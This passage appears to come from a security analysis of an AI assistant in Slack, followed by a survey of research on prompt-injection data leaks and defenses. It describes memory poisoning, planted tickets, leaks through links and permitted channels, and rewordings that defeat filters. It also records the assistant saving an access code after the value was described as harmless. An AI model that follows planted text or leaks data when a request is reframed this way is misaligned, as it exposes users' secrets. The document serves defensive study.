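Claude's memory was less strictly limited by channel. The researchers had Claude save a made-up fact in one public channel. When a different user who had never joined that channel asked about the fact in another public channel, Claude repeated it word for word and linked to the original message. Later it brought up the fact in answer to a general question and added that other people had recently asked about it. A fact saved in a private channel did not appear in a public one.

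No link or outside server was involved, so Agent Proxy had nothing to block. Most employees can already read public channels, which limits the harm to secrecy. Misinformation is the greater danger, because anyone who can talk to Claude in a public channel could save a false instruction, such as the wrong procedure for approving refunds, and Claude might later give it to colleagues who never saw where it came from. Claude refused to save a value described as an access code, but agreed once the researchers described the same value as harmless.

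Under the December rules, notes about one channel stay in that channel. Claude can still save workspace notes from any public channel, and it reads them in every channel, including private ones. The fact in the July test could therefore still spread if Claude saved it as a workspace note rather than a channel note. Users can reduce the risk by asking Claude to remember something "for this channel", and owners can inspect and delete workspace notes.

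The new rules create a different risk when a private channel becomes public. In July, Anthropic said new sessions would no longer read the notes saved while the channel was private. Now the notes stay with the channel and Claude keeps using them, so someone who joins later could ask for them. Before opening a private channel, members should have Claude list its notes and delete those that newcomers shouldn't see.

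### Scheduled jobs and gaps in the log

One channel member created a job that posted every day with a single request. Claude didn't ask for confirmation, and no second person had to approve the job. Any member can change or pause a job like this, and it keeps running after its creator leaves the company unless someone also removes that person from the channel. However, Claude refused to create a job when the instruction came from a planted ticket.

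A scheduled job can post long after anyone has thought about its audience. A weekly summary might suit a channel of ten people but not the same channel after 50 more have joined. In July, the administrators' page didn't show who had created a job. Anthropic has since added the creator's name, which makes old jobs easier to review, but it still doesn't describe any approval step before a new job starts.

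Administrators may also have trouble finding out what Claude did. The network log omits GitHub traffic and MCP connections, including those Claude uses to post in Slack. When Claude created a GitHub issue during the tests, Pluto Security found no log entry for it in that hour or the surrounding hours. The log is useful for checking the proxy's rules but could miss a message that leaked information.

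Anthropic now describes the log as "best effort" and warns that a missing entry doesn't prove that Claude made no request. Enterprise customers can also read full transcripts, including each tool call, through a separate API. Other customers have to trace a post by combining the Slack thread with the logs of each connected tool, and they should practice this before an incident.

### Links that the proxy doesn't check

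Agent Proxy controls which sites the sandbox can contact, but not which addresses Claude can write in a message. Suppose an attacker's ticket gets past Claude's defenses and asks for a customer's account number:

| What Claude might do with the number | Effect of Agent Proxy |
|---|---|
| Send it from the sandbox to outside.example.com | Blocks the request, unless a setting allows that site |
| Put it in a link to outside.example.com and post the link in Slack | None on the link |
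| Write it in a Slack message that outsiders can read | None on the text |
| Include it in a comment on a public GitHub project | None, because GitHub traffic uses a separate proxy |

In June, Anthropic wrote that data could leave the sandbox only for hosts that the company had allowed. That describes the sandbox's web requests, but posting a Slack message also sends data out of the sandbox. If Slack then fetches a preview of a link in the message, the request comes from Slack's network, where Agent Proxy's rules don't apply.

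Pluto Security came across these requests while testing the proxy. When the researchers pasted their test addresses into Slack, Slack's servers requested those addresses, and the researchers had to exclude the visits from their results. Pluto Security reports no similar test of a link that Claude, rather than a person, posted, and Anthropic's documentation for Claude Tag doesn't make clear whether Claude's posts turn previews off. In PromptArmor's February test, a volunteer reported no preview request from the Claude app in Slack, but Claude Tag has since replaced that app.

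A company can find out by repeating Rehberger's server-log test with links that Claude posts in a test channel, both in a new message and in a thread reply. If Claude refuses to write the link, the test shows nothing about previews. The test is worth repeating occasionally because Anthropic warns that features may change during the beta.

Claude Tag has no documented setting for turning previews off if they are on, and colleagues can click a harmful link either way. The company's best protection is to keep private data away from channels where Claude reads strangers' text. For example, customers' tickets could arrive in a channel where Claude has no access to accounts, while a few employees look up accounts with Claude in a separate private channel. The company should also limit Claude's Slack search in the ticket channel to channels Claude has joined, and check the workspace notes, since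 either could give an attacker information from elsewhere. If Claude can write to GitHub from the ticket channel, it shouldn't also be able to read private repositories from there, because a planted instruction could then cause a leak like GitLost.

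## Experiments on filters for outgoing data

In controlled tests, limiting where an agent can send data has worked better than searching the data for secrets. The most direct comparison is *The Framing Gap* (August 2026), by Rahman and Kim. They asked an agent to summarize a web page and measured the attack success rate, which is how often, as a percentage, instructions planted on the page made the agent leak a secret.

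### The same request in different words

The agent's working text included an invented session token and a rule against sending it anywhere but one trusted server. The agent could take a single action, either sending data to a web address or finishing with a reply. The tools only recorded what the agent tried to do, so nothing left the researchers' machine. In each trial the agent read a clean page and a page with planted text, and Rahman and Kim counted a success only if the planted text caused it. They tested six models, running 20 trials of each attack on the main models and 10 on the others.

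GPT-4o never leaked the token in 200 trials of ten obvious attacks, such as a direct order or a command hidden in the page's HTML. The researchers then reworded one attack in seven ways, keeping its goal but never asking the agent to disclose a secret. Some versions presented the token as a routine part of a request, such as a checksum or a configuration value, and others gave the attacker's server a name similar to the trusted server's. Two of the seven worked every time. Across all seven and the original, GPT-4o leaked the token in 40% of trials. Rewording raised the rate sharply on five of the six models, and the rate reached 86.2% on Gemma 2 9B.

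Small changes in wording greatly affected the success rate. Five paraphrases of the checksum version had success rates from 0 to 100%, averaging 52%, and an attacker who tried three of them would have about a 96% chance of succeeding. Finding a new pretext that worked was much harder, and the 13 tested failed in all 130 trials. A benchmark that uses only one wording could therefore make the same agent look completely safe or completely unsafe.

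The confidentiality rule made little difference. GPT-4o leaked the token in 31.9% of reworded trials with the rule and 38.1% without it, a smaller gap than the researchers saw between two identical runs. They conclude that the model mistook the planted text for part of its task, rather than overcoming a refusal. This fits the role confusion that Ye and colleagues measured inside models.

Rahman and Kim also tried some of their pages on the ChatGPT product, which leaked nothing in 48 trials. They couldn't tell which safeguard was responsible. In *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026), Yang, Na and Choi got a deployed ChatGPT model to follow planted text in 121 of 168 attempts. They counted every case where the model followed the text, not only leaks, so the two rates aren't comparable. Still, their result is a reason not to treat 0 leaks in 48 trials as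 proof of immunity.

### How the defenses compared

Rahman and Kim tested these defenses against the reworded requests:

| Defense | Model and trials | Attack success rate | Effect on normal work |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rule against disclosing the token | GPT-4o, 160 | 31.9% | Not measured |
| Rule that lists forbidden uses and adds "in any form" | GPT-4o, 120 | 0% | Not measured |
| The same list without "in any form" | GPT-4o, 80 | 48.8% | Not measured |
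| No defense | Llama 3.1 8B, 80 | 21.2% | Not measured |
| Page text in a separate input channel | Llama 3.1 8B, 80 | 38.8% | Not measured |
| SecAlign, a fine-tuned model | Llama 3.1 8B, 80 | 32.5% | Not measured |
| Planner/reader split | Llama 3.1 8B, 80 | 0% | 9 of 10 summaries acceptable |
| Destination allow-list | Follows from the design | 0% | Blocks legitimate requests to other servers |

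The broad confidentiality rule is the easiest defense to add, since it takes only a few more words in the prompt, but it is fragile. Removing the catch-all phrase let almost half the attacks through, even though the prompt still prohibited signing, encoding, logging, appending or transmitting the token. A company that uses such a rule relies on the model to recognize that it covers every new pretext.

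SecAlign trains a model to ignore instructions in its data channel. The trained model resisted a standard injection in all 20 trials, while the undefended model followed it every time. But this resistance didn't carry over to reworded requests in an agent with tools. Each condition had only one run, so the results don't show that SecAlign made the agent worse than no defense.

The planner/reader split uses two models. The planner chooses the agent's actions without access to the page, which is summarized by a reader that has no access to the token. Planted text can therefore influence only a model that has no secret to leak. The 90% score for normal work comes from an easy case, because the agent's plan didn't depend on anything in the page. A support agent would be harder to divide this way because it has to read a ticket before it can look up the right account.

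The researchers also built an output filter that blocked any request carrying the token to an untrusted server. They tested it with planted text that asked for the token in encoded form. The first version searched for an exact copy of the token, and 50.0% of attacks got through, compared with 56.7% without a filter. The second version undid five kinds of disguise, including reversed text and two common encodings, before searching, and it stopped all of those attacks.

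The researchers then tried ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one 13 places along in the alphabet, so that "DEMO" becomes "QRZB". The token got through in all 20 trials because the filter wasn't built to undo ROT13. They could add ROT13 to the encodings the filter undoes, but GPT-4o could reliably produce five of the six encodings they tested, and an attacker can make up others. A Slack filter that redacts secrets has the same weakness.

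Checking the incoming page worked better. A second model, told exactly what kind of instruction to look for, flagged all 80 pages with planted text and none of the clean ones. Rahman and Kim call this result an upper bound because a real attacker could use a trick the detector's prompt doesn't describe.

### Why the allow-list scored zero

The allow-list has zero leaks because this comparison counts a leak only when the agent sends the token to a server other than the trusted one, and the allow-list blocks all requests to other servers. Encoding the token or splitting it across several requests makes no difference, because the check never reads the data. However, the definition doesn't count a token that the agent writes in its reply.

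That omission matters for an agent that posts to #support, because colleagues read its replies. The agent can't post unless Slack is on the allow-list. If it puts an account key in a message, the allow-list accepts the request because Slack is a permitted destination, even if half the channel has no right to see the key. GitLost also leaked private text through a permitted destination. Any links in the message need a separate check, as with Claude Tag's Agent Proxy.

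Designers of more elaborate destination checks accept the same limit. Lim, Chang and Lee (2026), in *SPILLWAY*, describe a check that allows a message only if the user named the recipient or a trusted tool returned it in a dedicated field, such as an email's sender. They state that no check on destinations can stop planted content from being sent to a legitimate recipient. Fixing the agent's plan in advance doesn't prevent this either. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) gives the example of an agent that reads a calendar and emails the result to a colleague. Planted text in the calendar can still change the content of the email, though not its recipient.

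### A small model and simple filters

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay tested cruder filters in February 2026. Their agent automatically loaded a preview of any link the user mentioned, and they planted instructions in the linked page's title, description, body or link text. In 480 runs, the agent sent private data to their server 423 times (88.1%). In 95% of those cases, its reply to the user looked harmless, so a filter that read only the reply would have found nothing.

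They then tested each defense in 30 runs of one attack:

| Defense | Runs in which data got out |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Instruction to treat web content as data | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% |
| Both | 56.7% |
| Domain allow-list | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% |

No leaks got past any of the four filters, but the results aren't equally convincing. The allow-list faced an attempted leak in every run and blocked them all. The block on suspicious addresses rejected any path containing the word "collect", which appeared in the researchers' own sample attack. Without a defense, the agent attempted a leak in every run. It did so in only 23.3% of runs with the keyword filter and in none with the filter for random-looking values, so the test provides almost no evidence about whether that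 last filter works. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking values while the filter was on, but they don't explain how the model would have known about a filter that ran outside it.

The high overall rate also needs careful interpretation, because all the runs used one small model, qwen2.5:7b, with the secret placed directly in its working text and hardly any safety instructions. Lan and colleagues call this set-up "attacker-favorable". They did not test whether the filters would interrupt legitimate requests. In 120 trials with clean pages, the agent never contacted their server, so the leaks weren't random errors.

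Test software can distort results for small models in other ways. *Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation* (2026) re-examined a reported attack success rate of 62.8% for llama3.1:8b. The rate fell to 0% with corrected software, even though the model read the planted text in 41 of 43 attacks. The earlier figure came largely from faulty scoring and attacks that never reached the model.

Lan and colleagues also had the agent split a key into four pieces and send each in a separate request. The share of runs with a recognizable leak in the first request fell from 96.7% to 26.3%, though the agent also more often failed to send anything. The build bot's limit of one summary per build is meant to prevent a key from being split across messages in the same way in Slack.

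### The 2025 figures and what came after

The first detailed measurements of agents leaking personal data are now mainly of historical interest. In *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents*, Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues (2025) used AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an agent's workplace and plants instructions in the data the agent reads. They gave six models, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, 16 banking tasks and four planted requests to email the customer's data to an attacker. Attacks succeeded about 20% of the time on average, and most models' task completion rates fell by 15 to 50 percentage points under attack. With 48 tasks and GPT-4o alone, attacks succeeded about 15% of the time.

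The models were less likely to reveal passwords than other data. A request for the password alone failed on every model but one, while a request that omitted the password succeeded 93% of the time against Claude 3.5 Sonnet. Rahman and Kim similarly found a year later that calling the token a credential stopped an otherwise effective attack. A model's tendency to withhold passwords therefore does little to protect the addresses and account balances in an ordinary support ticket.

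Alizadeh and colleagues also tried AgentDojo's built-in defenses on GPT-4o. Two of them, a classifier for planted instructions and a prompt that repeats the user's request, stopped every attack on the 16 tasks, but neither stopped every attack on the 48. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) recalculated results from older GPT-4o runs across AgentDojo and found that the classifier cut attack success to 7.9% but also cut the share of tasks completed from 67.1% to 42.1%. Limiting the agent to the tools its task needed cut attack success to 6.5% without reducing task completion.

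All these tests used fixed attacks, but a real attacker can reword an attack that fails. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) has since automated this process by having a language model repeatedly rewrite planted text, with no feedback except whether each version had worked. PIGuard, a classifier that had blocked every fixed attack on a GPT-4o-mini agent, let through 28.0% of the rewritten ones. The paper also cites work by Nasr and colleagues in which attackers who knew everything about the model and its defense had success rates above 90% against many published defenses.

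He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *AttriGuard*, gave the attacker up to 200 attempts at each of 61 test cases. Their attacker knew how the defense worked and could see which actions it had blocked. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, the results were:

| Defense | How it works | Fixed attacks | Adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | Classifies incoming text | 4.9% | 52.5% |
| PromptArmor | Has a model delete planted instructions | 0% | 29.5% |
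| MELON | Reruns the agent with the user's task hidden | 0% | 82.0% |
| AttriGuard | Reruns the agent with outside text reworded | 0% | 6.6% |

He and colleagues developed AttriGuard, so they had a reason to want it to do well, but they gave the attacker a full description of it. Raising the limit to 500 attempts increased the attack success rate against MELON to 90.2% and left the rate against AttriGuard unchanged. A 0% success rate for fixed attacks is poor evidence of what a persistent attacker could do.

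### AgentDojo's Slack tasks

AgentDojo's Slack tasks closely resemble work in a team channel. The agent reads and sends messages and opens web pages and files in a simulated workspace. A user might ask it to summarize a page and send the summary to a colleague, while the page contains an attacker's instructions to do something else. *SecOPD* (2026) reports that 105 of the benchmark's 949 tests are Slack tests. Each test pairs one user task with one attacker's goal. Researchers report how often the attacker succeeds and how many user tasks the agent completes with and without an attack.

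Undefended agents have often failed these tests. In tests by He and colleagues, attacks succeeded more than 75% of the time against both GPT-4.1-mini and Qwen3-32B. *Will the User Ever Know?* (2026) reports success rates from 76% to 100% across four models. One of them, Qwen3-235B, followed 96.2% of Slack attacks but only 32.5% of those in longer office tasks. The paper attributes this gap to Slack tasks being short and simple, which gives the agent fewer chances to skip the planted text.

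Newer models may resist the standard attacks much better. In *GRAD* (October 2026), only one of 20 Slack attacks succeeded against an undefended DeepSeek Flash agent, which completed 85% of its tasks under attack. The sample is small and the attacks were fixed, but the result suggests that the rates above 75% aren't a fair guide to current agents.

AttriGuard checks each action by running the agent a second time, after a helper model has rewritten the outside text to turn commands into plain descriptions. If the agent still proposes much the same action, AttriGuard allows it, because the user's request was probably the cause. Otherwise, AttriGuard blocks the action because planted text probably caused it. In a test on the Slack tasks with five helper models, attacks succeeded at most 1.05% of the time. The agent completed 74 to 84% of the tasks when there was no attack and 47 to 60% when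 there was one.

Across all of AgentDojo, the cost in completed tasks depended on the agent's model:

| Defense | Gemini 2.5 Flash | Llama 3.3 70B | Average time per task, Gemini |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 57.6% | 59.8% | 11.5 s |
| AttriGuard | 67.4% | 54.4% | 32.4 s |
| CaMeL | 38.0% | 37.0% | 165.5 s |

CaMeL is the full design behind Rahman and Kim's planner/reader split. Like AttriGuard, it stopped every fixed attack, but the agent completed about a third fewer tasks than without a defense. This drop is a more realistic estimate of the loss in usefulness than the 90% score in Rahman and Kim's single-step test.

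SPILLWAY, the newest of these defenses, also had a 0% attack success rate on the Slack tasks with three models. Lim and colleagues tested four groups of AgentDojo tasks on each model, and no standard attack succeeded in any of the 12 combinations. Two earlier defenses, MELON and Progent, each let at least one attack through in 11 of them. Yet Progent, which restricts the tools an agent may call, was the one strong defense that Ma and colleagues couldn't weaken on GPT-4o-mini. A defense's score can therefore change a lot with the set-up. Lim and colleagues also tested SPILLWAY against attacks produced by automated rewriting, but they replayed attacks that others had prepared instead of letting an attacker adapt to SPILLWAY.

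A score of zero on these tasks doesn't mean that an agent's posts are accurate. AgentDojo mostly tests whether the agent takes an action the attacker wants, such as sending data to an outsider. He et al. removed the cases where the attacker only wanted to change the agent's text. AttriGuard also allows the wording to differ between its two runs, because summaries vary even without an attack. The false claim about the release team in the #builds report could appear in both runs and pass.

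Links are also a weak point. Every adaptive attack that beat AttriGuard aimed to make the agent visit a certain website. The attacker only had to suggest that the site had more information, without ordering the agent to go there. An agent writing a summary could have just as good a reason to include such a link.

### Removing code or links by itself

No published experiment seems to measure how much protection comes from removing code blocks or links alone. The closest test of an outgoing filter is in *Beyond Static Sandboxing* (2026), where a second model checked an agent's text for dangerous commands. The filter caught all four harmful samples and passed all three safe ones, but seven samples are far too few to estimate an error rate. It also blocked whole answers instead of removing the code. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) describes a test in which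 planted text got links and images into an agent's report, but the test didn't include a filter to remove them.

Other researchers have tested removal on the text an agent reads. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter*, trained a model to delete planted instructions from incoming text. It cut attack success from over 40% to about 2% and reduced performance on normal work by about 1%, though they didn't test attacks optimized by computer. AttriGuard's weakest setting is closer to code removal because it rewrites code-like structures as ordinary sentences in the copy used for the second run. Attacks still succeeded 12.2% of the time with that setting. Neither result shows what would happen if a filter removed code from the finished message.

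The build agent from the Slack filter example would be a good subject for the missing experiment. Researchers could save several hundred of its drafts, some written after it read ordinary logs and some after it read logs with planted text. They would then pass a copy of every draft through four versions of the filter, with all other steps turned off:

| | Links kept | Links removed |
|---|---|---|
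| **Code kept** | Version A | Version B |
| **Code removed** | Version C | Version D |

Let *p* be the share of planted drafts that still cause harm after filtering. The effect of removing only code is *p*(A) − *p*(C), and the effect of removing only links is *p*(A) − *p*(B). Version D would show whether removing both works better than removing either one alone. Testing every version on the same saved drafts makes the comparison fair, because a model may write a dangerous command in one run and refuse in the next.

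The researchers would have to count each kind of harm separately. They could post the filtered drafts in a test channel and use a server log to detect preview requests. A script could check whether an invented key was still readable. To measure the risk from commands, they could ask developers in a test environment to repair the build and record how many ran a harmless planted command. To measure how much the filters hindered normal work, they would give other developers reports from ordinary logs and compare how often and how quickly each group found the fault.

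The number of drafts tested matters most when a filter appears perfect. If none of *n* independent drafts causes harm, the upper 95% confidence limit on the true rate of harm is about 3/*n*. That limit is about 10% for 30 drafts and 1% for 300. The drafts would also need different wordings, since 300 near-copies of one attack would reveal little about how the filter handles other attacks.

A second stage should let an attacker see the results and try again, perhaps 200 times per case, as in the AttriGuard tests. Code removal would probably do well against commands in code blocks and much worse if the attacker got the agent to write the same command as an ordinary sentence. The agent should also run live in this stage, because it might respond to "[code removed]" by posting the command in another form. Rahman and Kim's filter judged only one action, so their results don't cover an agent that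 tries again.

Some drafts in both stages should contain a false statement but no code or link. All four versions would leave these drafts unchanged, and the developers' reactions would show how much harm an attacker can do without code or links.
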